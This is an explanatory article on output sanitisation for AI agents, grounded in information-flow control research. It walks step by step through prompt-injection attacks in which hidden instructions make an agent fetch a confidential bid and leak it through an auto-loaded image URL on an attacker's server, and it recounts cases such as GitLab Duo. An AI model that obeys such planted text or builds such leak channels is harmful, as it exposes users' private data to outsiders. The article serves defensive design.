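# When an AI agent's output needs no sanitisation: finding the places where data could leak

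## What output sanitisation is and how an agent's output can leak data

Output sanitisation is a security measure for software that runs on a language model, the kind of program behind chatbots such as ChatGPT. A sanitiser sits between the model and whatever receives its output. It removes, rewrites or blocks the parts that could do harm, such as a script that a browser would run or an image link whose web address contains a customer's account number. Web developers have long done something similar with strangers' comments on their sites, and the same reasoning applies to models because a stranger can often influence what a model writes.

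A sanitiser can delete links and pictures that the user wanted, and it needs maintenance. Whether a system needs one depends on what happens to the text after the model writes it. Judging that takes some knowledge of how agents work and how attackers misuse them.

### The agent loop

A language model takes in a piece of text, called its context, and writes a continuation. An agent is a language model that runs in a loop, with tools for reading data and taking actions. On each pass, the surrounding software assembles the context from the developer's standing instructions, the user's request and a record of everything so far. The model's continuation may be an answer for the user or a tool call. A tool call is a short piece of text in a fixed format that names a tool and its inputs, such as a mailbox search for the word "invoice". The software recognises the tool call, runs the search, adds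 the results to the context and starts the model again. The loop stops when the model writes an answer without a tool call.

The model only writes text, and other programs act on it, for example by opening a mailbox or contacting a website. A consumer is any program, person or agent that receives this output, directly or through another consumer. The search tool is a consumer of the model's query, and the chat window and the person reading it are consumers of the model's answer.

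### Prompt injection

A model's context is a single run of text. *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (2025) represents this as F(p‖d), where the model F runs on the developer's prompt p with outside data d appended. Whoever wrote d can include their own instructions. Prompt injection is text planted in material the model reads that makes it follow an attacker's instructions. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a 2025 article for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C gives the example of a recruiter who uses a model to score CVs. An applicant with no access to the recruiter's system can hide a line in the CV telling the model to approve it for interview, and the model may do so.

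The software developer Simon Willison explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025) that he named prompt injection after SQL injection, an older attack on databases. In SQL injection, an attacker types part of a database command into a web form, and a badly written program inserts it into its own command. Programmers can prevent this with parameterised queries, which set the command's structure before the user's input is added. David C thinks the comparison is dangerous because no such fix exists for models. A database engine handles commands and values differently, whereas a model only predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word). *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) attributes the difference to SQL's grammar, which lets a parser separate code from data. Natural language has no grammar that allows this, and developers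 train models to follow instructions wherever they appear.

Developers try to mark the boundary with tags that label each stretch of text in the context by role, such as the user's words or the contents of a fetched web page. Training is supposed to teach the model to obey only the user. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, tested whether the tags separate these roles inside the model. They trained a probe, a simple classifier that reads a model's internal activity, on identical passages inside different tags, so that it could learn only the tags' effect. When they put real user messages to chatbots inside tool tags, the probe still rated the text 76 to 88% likely to be the user's across four models, so the style of the text outweighed its tag. Attacks also succeeded more often when this confusion was greater. In 1,000 attempts to make an agent send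 out a secret file, the success rate rose from 2% where the planted command registered as least user-like to 70% where it registered as most user-like. The four models were of modest size, so the exact figures may not carry over to the strongest models of late 2026.

Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026) argue in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* that a perfect defence inside such a model is impossible in principle. Suppose an ideal observer sees one of the model's internal states and must guess whether it came from trusted or untrusted text, when both are equally likely. The observer's lowest possible error rate is ½(1 − TV), where TV, the total variation distance, is 0 if the two kinds of text produce identical distributions of states and 1 if the distributions never overlap. At a TV of 0.98, the observer still errs 1% of the time. The error rate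 reaches zero only when there is no overlap, so the impossibility result depends on there being some. Single words clearly overlap, since "send" enters the model as the same string of numbers whether it appears in an order or a newsletter. Pant and colleagues assume that the deeper states that drive decisions overlap too. Their theorem also doesn't cover systems in which a separate program decides which tool calls go ahead, and a sanitiser is likewise a separate program.

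Injections often fail. When Ye and colleagues hid a plain fake command in a web page, the attack succeeded at most 2% of the time on every model but one, where it reached 26%. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reports that most known attempts to extract secrets from ChatGPT fail because the model refuses. But it also describes a 2025 email, written as routine office correspondence about restructuring, that worked in half of the test runs. According to OpenAI, filters that sort incoming text into malicious and harmless usually miss attacks of that quality, because catching them means detecting a lie, often without the necessary background. Fortune (2025) reported that OpenAI thinks some attacks on AI browsers will probably persist. An attacker who can send a thousand emails needs only a low success rate, which is presumably why Willison calls 95% detection a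 failing grade in web security.

### What else an attacker needs

A successful injection gives the attacker influence over some text, but Willison says that stealing data requires all three of these conditions: the agent can access private data, it reads untrusted content, and it can communicate outward in a way that could send that data out. He counts almost any web request as outward communication, including one that loads an image, and even a link that the user has to click.

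His evidence is a long list of products in which researchers found the combination, including ChatGPT, Google Bard, Slack and GitHub Copilot Chat. He writes that the vendors fixed almost all of these cases promptly, usually by closing the outward route. This makes sense because people install a mail agent to read their private mail, much of which comes from outsiders. A vendor who removed either the access to private mail or the exposure to outsiders' text would have little product left. The outward route is often incidental, so vendors can close it without users noticing much.

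OpenAI reached a similar position in March 2026 using source-sink analysis, an established method in security engineering. An attacker needs a source, which is a way to influence the system, and a sink, which is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context. Following a link, sending information to a third party or using a tool can be a sink. In Willison's terms, the untrusted content is the source, the outward route is the sink, and the private data is what the attacker wants to steal.

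OpenAI's notion of a sink is broader than Willison's third condition because it includes tools that can do damage without disclosing anything. An exfiltration sink is a consumer that lets an unauthorised party learn something from the output. An execution sink is a consumer, such as a database or a shell (a program that runs typed commands), that acts on the output, whether or not data leaks. A consumer can be both. For example, a shell can delete a folder or upload one.

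### A leak, step by step

Suppose staff at a construction firm use an agent to search and summarise company email. The firm is about to bid €412,000 to replace a school roof, and a rival wants to know the figure.

1. The rival sends the firm an ordinary enquiry about subcontracting. Lower down, in white letters on a white background, the message contains an instruction for the model: look up the bid, and end the summary with a picture whose address, on a server that the rival owns, includes the figure.
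2. An employee asks the agent to summarise the morning's mail. The mail tool returns the new messages, and the rival's text enters the context with the rest.
3. The model follows the planted instruction and writes another tool call, a search for the bid. Now the figure is in the context too.
4. The model writes a perfectly decent summary and, underneath, the code for a picture. The picture's address ends in `/logo.png?n=412000`.
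5. The chat window formats the answer for display. The employee's browser comes to the picture code and requests the picture from the rival's server, as browsers routinely do for pictures on web pages. Nobody clicks on anything.
6. The server returns a transparent image one pixel wide and adds a line to its log: `GET /logo.png?n=412000`. The rival opens the log and reads the bid.

The browser sent the figure out at step 5. If the chat window had displayed the answer as plain text, the employee would have seen an odd line of code below the summary, and the rival's log would have stayed empty, even though the injection had made the model write exactly what the rival wanted.

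### What a sanitiser does about it

In this firm, a sanitiser would sit between steps 4 and 5. It could remove the picture code, either always or only when the address is not on an allowlist, which is a list of the only destinations a program may contact. The summary would still arrive intact, without the picture.

It could encode the output instead, which means replacing characters that have a special function with codes for displaying them. In HTML, the language of web pages, an angle bracket opens an instruction to the browser, so an encoder swaps it for a code that only displays a bracket. But many chat windows accept pictures in Markdown, a shorthand that uses square brackets and parentheses, which HTML encoding doesn't change. If the window converts Markdown to HTML after the encoder has run, the browser still loads the picture, which leaks the figure.

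The sanitiser could instead block the answer. A simple version rejects any output that does not fit an expected format, and the Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre recommends this check before any output goes downstream. ChatGPT has a more selective version, which OpenAI calls Safe Url. It looks for cases where information from the conversation would be sent to a third party. ChatGPT then either shows the user that information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the transmission and tells the agent to find another way to do the job.

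The standard reference for such measures comes from OWASP, the Open Worldwide Application Security Project, a non-profit that publishes ranked lists of software risks. Its *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* covers insufficient validation, sanitisation and handling of a model's output before it passes to other components. OWASP advises developers to treat the model like any other user and to validate its responses before they reach internal functions, following its general verification standard. Developers should encode output that goes back to users and use parameterised queries for database operations. Web pages should have a strict content security policy (CSP), which limits the sites from which the browser may load material for the page. Developers should also log outputs and watch for unusual patterns.

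OWASP's list also asks for encoding "based on where the LLM output will be used", with HTML encoding for web content and SQL escaping for database queries. This is the item most relevant to when a sanitiser is worth having, because it implies that whether a piece of text is dangerous depends on where it is used. For example, the line of picture code that gave away the roofing bid is harmless in a database field, as is a fragment of SQL in a chat window.

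Most of the entry concerns execution sinks. Its common examples include model output that runs in a shell, scripts that run in a reader's browser and unchecked database commands. Only one of its six attack scenarios involves sending private data to an attacker's server. In that scenario, a tool that summarises websites processes a planted instruction, and the model encodes sensitive content and sends it. OWASP does not identify the program that sends the data, which a developer would need to find.

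The August 2026 edition, in which the entry is numbered LLM10:2026, is more specific. According to the security company Invicti, in *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), the entry now expressly covers programs that automatically fetch outside resources named in a model's output, as a channel for exfiltration. It also covers terminals, the text windows in which programmers work, because they act on control codes hidden in the text they display. The entry fell from fifth place to last. OWASP based three-quarters of the ranking on a vote among practitioners and the rest on a collection of 7,714 recorded incidents. Advait Patel, who created another OWASP project, told ReversingLabs that the entry dropped "because everything above it got more urgent, not because output handling got safe". The ranking shows only relative urgency, so the fall is not evidence that developers can stop sanitising.

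If encoding has to suit the destination, a developer needs to know the destinations before choosing a sanitiser. Some of them may have no way of passing anything on to an outsider, and if nothing downstream can leak data, there may be no leak for a sanitiser to prevent.

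## The conditions under which a sanitiser protects nothing

A sanitiser against leaks is useful only if someone who isn't allowed to see the data can learn something about it from the output. A developer can check this by comparing the people and systems that can see the output with those allowed to see the data.

The authorised readers of an output, written R, are those who may see every piece of data that went into it. To find R, the developer lists the permitted readers of each item in the model's context and keeps only the names that appear on every list:

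R = readers(d₁) ∩ readers(d₂) ∩ … ∩ readers(dₙ)

Here d₁ to dₙ are the items in the context, and ∩ means the members the sets share. Everyone may read a public item, so public items remove nobody from R.

The observers of a consumer c, written Obs(c), are everyone who can learn something from the output once it reaches c. They include the people who look at c directly and the observers of any consumer c passes the output to. Finding them all in a real product requires listing everything downstream of c.

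Data can leak through a consumer c only if at least one observer in Obs(c) is missing from R. Even then, a leak isn't certain, because the part of the output that reaches that observer may contain nothing private. If Obs(c) is a subset of R for every consumer c, a sanitiser against leaks protects nothing, because nobody can learn anything they weren't entitled to know, even if an attacker controls every word the model writes.

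### A worked example

Nadia, an estimator at the roofing firm, asks the agent whether the school bid still makes a profit at a tile supplier's new prices. Besides her question, the context contains the bid spreadsheet and an email from the supplier. Nadia, Tom (the director) and Ewa (who runs the firm's computers) may read the spreadsheet. Lars, a salesman at the supplier, sent the email to Nadia, Ewa and Owen, the site manager. Only Nadia and Ewa may read both, so R = {Nadia, Ewa}.

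The output has three consumers:

| Consumer | Observers |
|---|---|
| Mail search on the firm's own server, whose records Ewa can open | Ewa |
| Chat window that displays plain text | Nadia |
| Folder of plain-text notes where the agent saves its answer | Nadia, Ewa |

Every observer is in R. Suppose Lars's email contains a planted instruction, and the model follows it by writing the bid into the address of a picture. Nadia sees a line of odd code, which also goes into the notes, and Lars learns nothing. A sanitiser that removed the picture code would tidy the answer without changing who knows the bid.

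A month later a colleague sets up a program that emails a weekly digest of new notes to everyone working on the school roof, including Owen and Lars. The agent, the model and the folder's permissions haven't changed, but Obs(notes folder) is now {Nadia, Ewa, Owen, Lars}, and two of those people are not in R. Stripping pictures wouldn't help, because Lars can read the bid in the agent's sentences. A sanitiser would have to recognise the bid in any wording, so it's simpler to leave the agent's notes out of the digest.

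The same folder and digest would be harmless if the context had held only Lars's email and Nadia's question about it, because all four people are allowed to read both. So whether a consumer is an exfiltration sink depends on both the consumer and the data behind the particular output.

R can also be stricter than necessary. The agent's answer might draw only on the supplier's prices, yet the calculation treats it as though it contained the bid. *Sightline* (2026) calls this problem label creep. It occurs because no code describes what happens inside a model call, so an analyst cannot see which inputs the answer used. The error is on the side of caution, but it may lead a developer to keep an unnecessary sanitiser.

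### Where the test comes from

The test is an application of information-flow control, which means labelling data by who may read it and how far to trust it, and checking the labels before each action. Dorothy Denning (1976), in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, gave the field its mathematical form. She assigned every stored item to a security class and defined a relation A → B, which holds when information in class A may flow into class B. An operator ⊕ gives the class of anything that a program computes from several inputs. A program may then write a value computed from a₁ to aₙ into b only if

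class(a₁) ⊕ … ⊕ class(aₙ) → class(b)

Denning showed that such classes form a lattice, so any two have a single least upper bound (⊕), the least restrictive class that keeps the restrictions of both. When each class is a set of readers, ⊕ is the intersection of the two sets, and information may flow only to places that add no new readers.

She also required the relation to be transitive, so that if data may move from A to B and from B to C, it may also move from A to C. Otherwise a program could move data from A to C through B even when moving it directly is forbidden. This matters for Obs(c) in the weekly digest example, where saving the answer to the folder is safe only if everything that reads the folder is safe too.

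Myers and Liskov (1997), in *A Decentralized Model for Information Flow Control*, came very close to the reader-and-observer test. In their model, each owner of a piece of data lists who may read it, and the "effective reader set" is the intersection of those lists. A program may write the data to an output channel only if everyone who can read the channel is in that set. An owner can declassify the data by adding readers to their own list. If the firm decided to tell Lars the bid, it would declassify the bid, and R would grow.

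A stronger idea, noninterference, defines security by what outsiders see. According to Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, one group of users does not interfere with another if nothing the first group does affects what the second group can see. Formally, take any sequence of commands w, and let w′ be the same sequence with the first group's commands deleted. Then for every user u in the second group,

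output(w, u) = output(w′, u)

The same comparison works for data. Suppose the rival is the second group, and the agent runs once with a bid of €412,000 and once with a bid of €430,000. If anything on the rival's screen or in its server log differs between the runs, the bid has interfered with what the rival sees.

When no outsider observes any consumer, the output cannot interfere with what outsiders see, provided that Obs(c) covers every way of learning from the output, including indirect ones. Denning excluded covert channels, such as a program's effect on the load of a shared computer, and Myers and Liskov excluded timing. A developer who needs protection against these has to add them to Obs(c).

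### FIDES: checking labels while an agent runs

Costa, Köpf and colleagues at Microsoft applied these ideas to agents in a system called FIDES, described in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025). FIDES attaches two labels to each piece of data. The confidentiality label can be a set of authorised readers, and when two items are combined, only readers authorised for both may read the result. The integrity label is "trusted" or "untrusted", and a single untrusted input makes the result untrusted. Nobody can trace precisely which inputs influenced a language model's response, so FIDES gives the response the combined label of everything in the model's context.

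Ordinary program code, which planted text cannot persuade, checks the labels against two policies before a tool runs:

1. A consequential action may go ahead only if the data behind the call is trusted.
2. A tool may send data out only if everyone who can read the channel may read the data.

Suppose Lars's email tells the agent to reply with the bid. The first policy blocks the reply because the context contains untrusted text, and the second blocks it because Lars is not in R. As Costa and colleagues point out, the second policy alone would not prevent an injection, but it limits the damage to flows that the labels allow. The first policy alone lets data go to unauthorised readers when the context is trusted, on the assumption that the user intended this. Later designs often require only one of the two policies for tools that send data. Examples are *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security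 and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) and *Flowsh* (2026), which restates both policies for a command shell.

The reader-and-observer test amounts to applying the second policy to a whole design in advance. If no consumer could violate the policy, there is no leak for a run-time check or a sanitiser to catch.

How far FIDES's guarantee applies elsewhere depends on its threat model. The attacker can tamper with data from untrusted sources and see the effects of some tool calls, but cannot watch the model's inputs and outputs directly. Costa and colleagues treat the user's messages as trusted and public, which would be the wrong label for a message describing the user's medical symptoms. They also treat replies to the user as inconsequential, so they place checks only before tool calls, although they say a developer can check replies too. In the earlier example, the roofing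 bid leaked through such a reply when the chat window loaded a picture. In a later article, *Information-flow control*, Microsoft suggests treating displayed links to hosts outside an allowlist as public channels, which would bring that chat window under the second policy.

FIDES guarantees explicit secrecy, which is weaker than noninterference. It blocks direct flows of secret data into places an attacker can see, but the agent's choices can still reveal something about that data. For example, an agent might open a rival's public price list only when its own firm's bid is above €400,000. The request contains no private data, but the rival's server log now reveals something about the bid. Costa and colleagues accept this because enforcing noninterference would essentially mean forbidding any publicly visible action after the agent had read anything secret. The rival counts as an observer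 of that request in the reader-and-observer test, so the test fails.

### What the checks achieved, and what they cost

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 user tasks and 36 attacker goals in four simulated settings: office work, travel, banking and the chat program Slack. They compared it with a basic agent that reads every tool result directly. FIDES hides untrusted results behind variable names, which the main model can pass on without reading the contents. When the contents need processing, a second model that has no tools can read them.

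With OpenAI's GPT-4o as the model and no policy checks, 152 injections succeeded against the basic agent and 21 against FIDES. With the checks on, none succeeded against either. These counts exclude cases that the benchmark scored as successes but the researchers judged harmless or misclassified on inspection.

The zero is less surprising than it looks because the researchers labelled a data field untrusted if any attack in the benchmark targeted it, which guaranteed that the labels were correct. A company labelling its own data doesn't know in advance where the attacks will be. Still, the result shows that the checks work as designed when the labels are correct, and it doesn't depend on how well GPT-4o resists the attacks.

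The checks also stopped legitimate work. This table gives the percentage of user tasks that each agent completed when nobody was attacking it:

| Setting | Basic agent, no checks | Basic agent, checks | FIDES, checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 75.0 | 37.0 | 59.0 |
| Travel | 70.0 | 73.0 | 41.0 |
| Banking | 98.8 | 37.5 | 52.5 |
| Slack | 93.3 | 20.0 | 47.6 |

Many banking tasks involve reading a file and following its instructions, which the checks are designed to prevent. In the travel tasks, the checks rarely interfered with the basic agent, but GPT-4o handled the hidden variables badly. FIDES completed 41% of the travel tasks with GPT-4o and 68% with OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model. Both models are old as of late 2026, so these completion rates are probably a poor guide to current agents.

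Kolluri and colleagues then built Prudentia, a version that gives the model information about the labels and policies so it can plan around them. On AgentDojo, it completed up to 9% more tasks than FIDES without human approval and cut required approvals by a factor of up to 1.9.

Microsoft released FIDES as an experimental feature of its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents. According to Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026), data from a tool that the developer forgot to label counts as trusted and public. Under that default, if the bid spreadsheet carries no label, R becomes everyone and every consumer passes the reader-and-observer test. A developer who takes R from a system's labels should therefore first check that the labels exist.

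### When there is no secret, no attacker or little room

A leak needs more than an observer outside R, and a design may rule out one of the other ingredients.

An agent that answers questions from published building regulations may have nothing secret in its context. R is then everyone, so any consumer is acceptable. But an attacker can sometimes bring a secret into the context. In the roofing example, the planted instruction made the agent search for the bid, which the employee had never mentioned. When checking for secrets, the developer therefore has to include everything the tools could fetch, whatever users type, and anything the agent remembers from earlier conversations.

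An agent might instead read only text from trusted colleagues, so that no attacker can influence what it writes, but it can still make mistakes. Microsoft gives the example of Alex, who asks an agent to deal with his unanswered email. Priya has sent him a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who isn't allowed to see the figures yet, has written to him too. Once the agent has read both messages, R is {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so a reply to Marco needs Alex's approval. If Priya had copied Marco in, R would be {Alex, Marco}, and the agent could send the reply by itself. Marco is only curious, and nobody has planted an instruction, but an unchecked agent might well tell him the numbers. *APPA* (2026), a related system, therefore assumes that invented facts or poor reasoning, like an injection, may lead a model to propose any tool call.

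Errors are probably a much rarer cause of leaks than attacks. *Observable Channels, Not Just Storage* (2026) measured how often agents from five model providers exposed private data through channels such as tool inputs. When the researchers removed explicit cues to extract the data, leakage fell sharply for all five. Errors also need a different defence. A model is unlikely to invent the address of a server that a rival owns, so a filter for picture links does little when there is no attacker, but a check on who receives each message would still catch the reply to Marco.

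Third, the output may be too narrow to carry much information. Suppose the firm's agent sorts incoming enquiries into four categories, and the mail system sends a different automatic reply for each. A rival who writes in is an observer outside R, but can learn from the reply only which of the four categories the model chose.

Information theory measures this in bits, where one bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) gives the capacity of a noiseless channel as log₂ of the number of outputs that can occur. For four labels, that is log₂ 4 = 2 bits per call. If the rival can also tell when the system rejects an invalid label, that fifth outcome raises the limit to log₂ 5, or about 2.3 bits.

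Leakage adds up over repeated calls. *Verifying LLM Inference to Detect Model Weight Exfiltration* (2025) bounds the leakage from a sequence by adding the log₂ of the number of allowed choices at each step. If the rival knows only that the bid is below €1 million, there are 1,000 possible values to the nearest thousand. Five enquiries with four possible answers each could be enough to identify the right one, since they distinguish 4⁵ = 1,024 cases. Ten could give the bid to the euro, since 4¹⁰ is 1,048,576. A rival who already knows that the bid is between €400,000 and €430,000 has only 31 values to distinguish, to the nearest thousand, and needs three enquiries.

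These are worst-case figures, which assume that the bid is in the context each time and that the model follows a planted code without error. But a sanitiser can't lower them, because every label is a legitimate output. Keeping the bid out of the sorting agent's context would prevent the leak, and limiting the number of enquiries per sender would slow the rival down.

A fixed format can still carry a lot of information. A ten-character reference code made of capital letters and digits allows 36¹⁰ values, or about 52 bits, enough for the whole bid in one message. The bound also covers only the output's content, so a rival who could time the replies might learn more.

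FIDES uses the same reasoning in reverse, to limit what an attacker can put into an agent. It ranks types of output by how much information they can carry, from a yes-or-no answer, to a choice from a fixed list, to free text. A policy can let the agent act on a yes-or-no answer drawn from an untrusted email, because the email's influence is limited to one bit. That bit can still do harm if it decides whether the agent pays an invoice.

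### Unnecessary, misplaced and ineffective sanitisers

"The sanitiser does nothing" can mean several things, and the remedies are different.

A sanitiser is unnecessary, at least as a defence against leaks, when no consumer of the output is an exfiltration sink, as with Nadia's agent before the digest. Microsoft's advice on when not to use FIDES describes a simple case, in which all inputs come from one trusted source and all outputs go to one trusted destination.

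A sanitiser doesn't help when the data leaves by another path. Suppose the firm strips pictures from every answer in the chat window, and the planted instruction tells the agent to open a web page whose address contains the bid. The bid leaves when the tool requests the page, before the model has written an answer to sanitise. *Silent Egress* (2026) demonstrated this type of leak by recording network traffic instead of reading the agent's text, and concluded that safety evaluations based on the text miss it. The web tool needs its own check, because a better picture filter would not stop the leak.

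An ineffective sanitiser sits on the path the data takes but lets the data through, like an HTML encoder that leaves Markdown images intact. Filters often fail this way because developers add patterns one at a time. *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (2026) describes the prevailing practice as an ad hoc fix for each newly discovered hiding place. It proposes measuring how many bits a set of adversarial encoders can still get past the monitor. Developers can then work to reduce that number without knowing which technique an attacker will try next.

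Some leaks contain no sensitive text for a filter to find. In *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) had an attacker share a page of true and invented records about a person and ask the agent to delete the entries that didn't match its files. The agent wrote nothing private, but the entries it left showed the attacker which records were true. Each kept or deleted entry reveals up to one bit. In tests with live Gmail and Notion accounts, 34.7% of the sensitive items leaked this way under a defence that uses a model to spot privacy violations. None leaked under the researchers' own system, FLOWSEAL, which intercepts every attempt to write or share and compares the destination with the records the agent has read. FLOWSEAL relies on a separate model to decide whether a message to an unknown recipient reveals a record, so it can also make mistakes.

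A developer can often tell the verdicts apart by attacking a test copy of the system with the sanitiser on and then off, while recording what each consumer sends. If data escapes both times, the record shows which path it took. The sanitiser is ineffective if the data went through the sanitised path, and misplaced if the data went around it. If nothing escapes either time, the sanitiser may be unnecessary or the attack may have been too weak. More attacks of the same kind won't show which explanation is right, so the developer has to go back to comparing Obs(c) with R.

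### Why a system without leaks can still do damage

Suppose Nadia's agent can also write commands for the firm's database of past bids, and only Nadia and Ewa can see the database or anything that comes out of it. The database passes the reader-and-observer test, but Lars's email could still make the agent delete every bid since 2019. No data would leak, because the database is an execution sink but not an exfiltration sink.

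*Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (2026) calls such weaknesses output-to-execution vulnerabilities, in which a browser, database or command interpreter runs a model's output as code. Parameterised queries protect a database when the model supplies only values, but *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (2026) notes that they are not enough when the model writes the command itself. It recommends giving the agent a read-only account, restricting which tables it may use and rejecting destructive commands. If the firm removed an HTML encoder because its pages could not leak data, it might also lose its protection against scripts that alter the page.

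FIDES has separate policies for preventing leaks and sabotage. In Microsoft's example, an agent sorts bug reports on GitHub. Its tool for posting public comments won't run once private data is in the context, which prevents a leak. Its tool for writing files won't run on untrusted input, which prevents sabotage. The comment tool would still post an attacker's text if everything in the context was public, and the file tool would still write a secret to a file if the secret came from a trusted source.

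An execution sink can also create an exfiltration sink. If the agent's database command could add an address to the digest's mailing list, a planted instruction could add the rival's address, and the next digest would send Nadia's notes to the rival. Goguen and Meseguer allowed for this in 1982 by including commands that change what users may do. In the reader-and-observer test, Obs(c) therefore has to include anyone the agent could add as an observer.

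## How to list everything that consumes the output

The reader-and-observer test misses any consumer that isn't on the list. An agent's developers will remember the chat window and the tools because they wrote them, but they're more likely to forget a program that somebody attached later, like the weekly digest.

One way to search systematically is to draw the system as a graph, with an arrow from each consumer to every other consumer it passes the output to. The observers of a consumer c are then

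Obs(c) = direct(c) ∪ Obs(c₁) ∪ … ∪ Obs(cₖ)

Here direct(c) is everyone who can look at c itself or who receives a request that c sends. The consumers that c's arrows point to are c₁ to cₖ, and ∪ combines the sets. For the roofing firm's notes folder, direct(c) was Nadia and Ewa, and the arrow to the digest added Owen and Lars.

### The procedure

1. List every form in which output leaves the model.
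2. For each form, list the consumers that receive it directly.
3. For each consumer, write down what it interprets, what it requests automatically, who can observe that, who runs it and which setting governs it.
4. Add everything the consumer passes the output to as a new consumer, and answer the same questions for that one.
5. Stop when a full pass adds nothing new.

The arrows can form a loop, for instance when an agent reads its own old notes. The search still ends, because each consumer goes on the list only once.

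Besides its final answer, an agent's output includes partial text shown while the model is still writing, the inputs (arguments) of tool calls, files, memory entries, error messages, and logs and traces, which record what the agent did at each step. Error messages and logs are easy to overlook because people rarely think of them as the agent's output. When a tool call fails, many programs copy its inputs into the error message to help engineers find the fault. Logs often store the model's raw text, so if the sanitiser sits between the model and the chat window, the log may still contain the picture link.

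A web page may interpret HTML or Markdown, a spreadsheet may treat a cell that begins with an equals sign as a formula, and another agent may treat an ordinary English sentence as an instruction. Automatic requests need a separate question because they happen without a click, as when the browser leaked the roofing bid by loading the picture. The observers include the people who read the text and whoever owns the server that receives such a request.

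It matters who runs the consumer because a company can inspect and change its own web page, but a supplier can change its product at any time. The supplier's staff may also be observers. If the team knows which setting controls the consumer's behaviour, it knows what to check again after an update. If nobody can name a setting, the behaviour may be a default that the supplier controls.

The list should include output forms that seem unrelated to the attacker's way in. Shim and colleagues built an attack in which the request arrives through one channel and the agent discloses the data in another. A defence that tracks consent within each conversation does not connect the request to the disclosure. So a support agent's ticket notes belong on the list even if attackers can only send email.

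### Partial text while the model is writing

Chat windows usually display an answer piece by piece, so a filter that needs the whole answer can't finish before the first words appear. AWS's *Configure streaming response behavior to filter content* describes how Guardrails, the filter in Amazon's Bedrock service for running models, handles this. By default, it holds back each piece until it has scanned it. In asynchronous mode, it sends the pieces to the user immediately, scans them in the background, and blocks later pieces if it finds a problem. This mode cannot mask sensitive information. If an early piece contained a picture link, a browser could request the picture before the filter blocked anything. The line of configuration that selects the mode therefore belongs in the team's list.

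Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft* (2025) describes a leak to which streaming contributed. GitLab is a site where programmers store code and review each other's changes, and Duo is its assistant. The researchers hid instructions in a public project. When a user asked Duo about that project, Duo read code changes from one of the user's private projects, encoded them and put them in a picture's address. When the user's browser requested the picture, the request carried the code to the researchers' server.

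GitLab already ran a widely used sanitiser called DOMPurify. But the page converted Markdown to HTML line by line, before the structure of the whole answer was available, so a tag could become active too early. Willison also describes the streaming display as a way around the filter. DOMPurify also keeps image tags by default, because its main purpose is to remove scripts. The overlooked consumer was the browser, which was acting on an unfinished answer. GitLab's patch stops Duo from displaying images and forms that point to domains outside gitlab.com, whichever of the two weaknesses lets a tag through.

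### A support assistant, consumer by consumer

Suppose a broadband company has a support assistant that reads customers' emails and account records and answers staff on an internal web page. It saves a summary of each case to a help-desk ticket and keeps short notes in a memory for later sessions. Anyone can try to plant instructions by emailing the company. Only support staff may read the account records.

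A first draft of the list would probably include the answer page and the account search. The table shows what the procedure might find. Round 1 lists the direct consumers of each output form, and each later round lists the consumers of those found in the previous round.

| Round | Consumer | Interprets | Requests automatically | Who can observe | Who runs it | Governing setting |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
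| 1 | Answer page, finished text | Markdown | Pictures | Staff member; owner of a picture's server | The company | Permitted Markdown; CSP |
| 1 | Answer page, partial text | Unfinished Markdown | Pictures, perhaps before a filter finishes | As for finished text | The company | Filter's streaming mode |
| 1 | Account search | Search terms | Nothing | Database administrators | The company | Permissions of the search tool |
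| 1 | Ticket summary | Formatted text, links | Nothing | Support staff; the customer, if the summary is public | Help-desk supplier | Default visibility of summaries |
| 1 | Assistant's memory | Nothing | Nothing | Anyone with access to the store | The company | Retention period; read permissions |
| 1 | Error tracker | Error text, including failed tool inputs | Unknown | Engineers; supplier's staff | Error-tracking supplier | Rules for removing private data |
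| 1 | Model provider's log viewer | Possibly Markdown | Unknown | Engineers; provider's staff | Model provider | Logging on or off |
| 2 | Email alert about a new summary | HTML | Pictures, in some mail programs | Everyone following the ticket, including an outside installer | Mail supplier | List of followers; alert template |
| 2 | Alert in the staff chat | Links | Link previews | Channel members; owner of the linked site | Chat supplier | Previews on or off |
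| 2 | Nightly spreadsheet of tickets | Formulas | Web data, if a formula asks for it | Analysts; owner of the site | The company | Importing cells as text |
| 2 | Later session that loads the memory | English | Whatever its tools can reach | Observers of that session's output | The company | The session's tools; which notes load |
| 2 | Help-desk agent that drafts replies | English | Web pages | The customer who receives the reply | Help-desk supplier | The agent's tools; approval before sending |
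| 3 | Customer's mail program | HTML | Pictures, link checks | The customer; anyone who gets the email from them | Customer's mail supplier | None the company controls |

The assistant has no tool for writing to customers, but its output can reach them in round 3. A customer could send an email containing an instruction that makes the assistant copy somebody else's address and payment history into the ticket summary. The help-desk agent then reads the summary, includes the details in its draft, and sends them to that customer. If summaries are public by default, the customer can read the details directly in the ticket.

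Finding these rows requires checking system records as well as asking colleagues what they use. The help-desk software will have a page of connected services, the ticket store will have a record of which accounts may read it, and the company's servers will have a schedule of exports. The team can enter "unknown" at this stage and use those entries to decide what to test.

### Why stored output keeps the search going

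The output's path can continue past a memory, a ticket or a shared file. These only store the text, but something with network access may read it weeks later.

Unit 42's *When AI Remembers Too Much* (2025) demonstrates this with a travel assistant. Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, built the assistant on Bedrock, gave it tools for booking trips and reading web pages, and switched on Bedrock's memory. At the end of each session, a model summarises the conversation. Bedrock stores the summary for up to 365 days and adds it to the agent's standing instructions whenever the same user returns.

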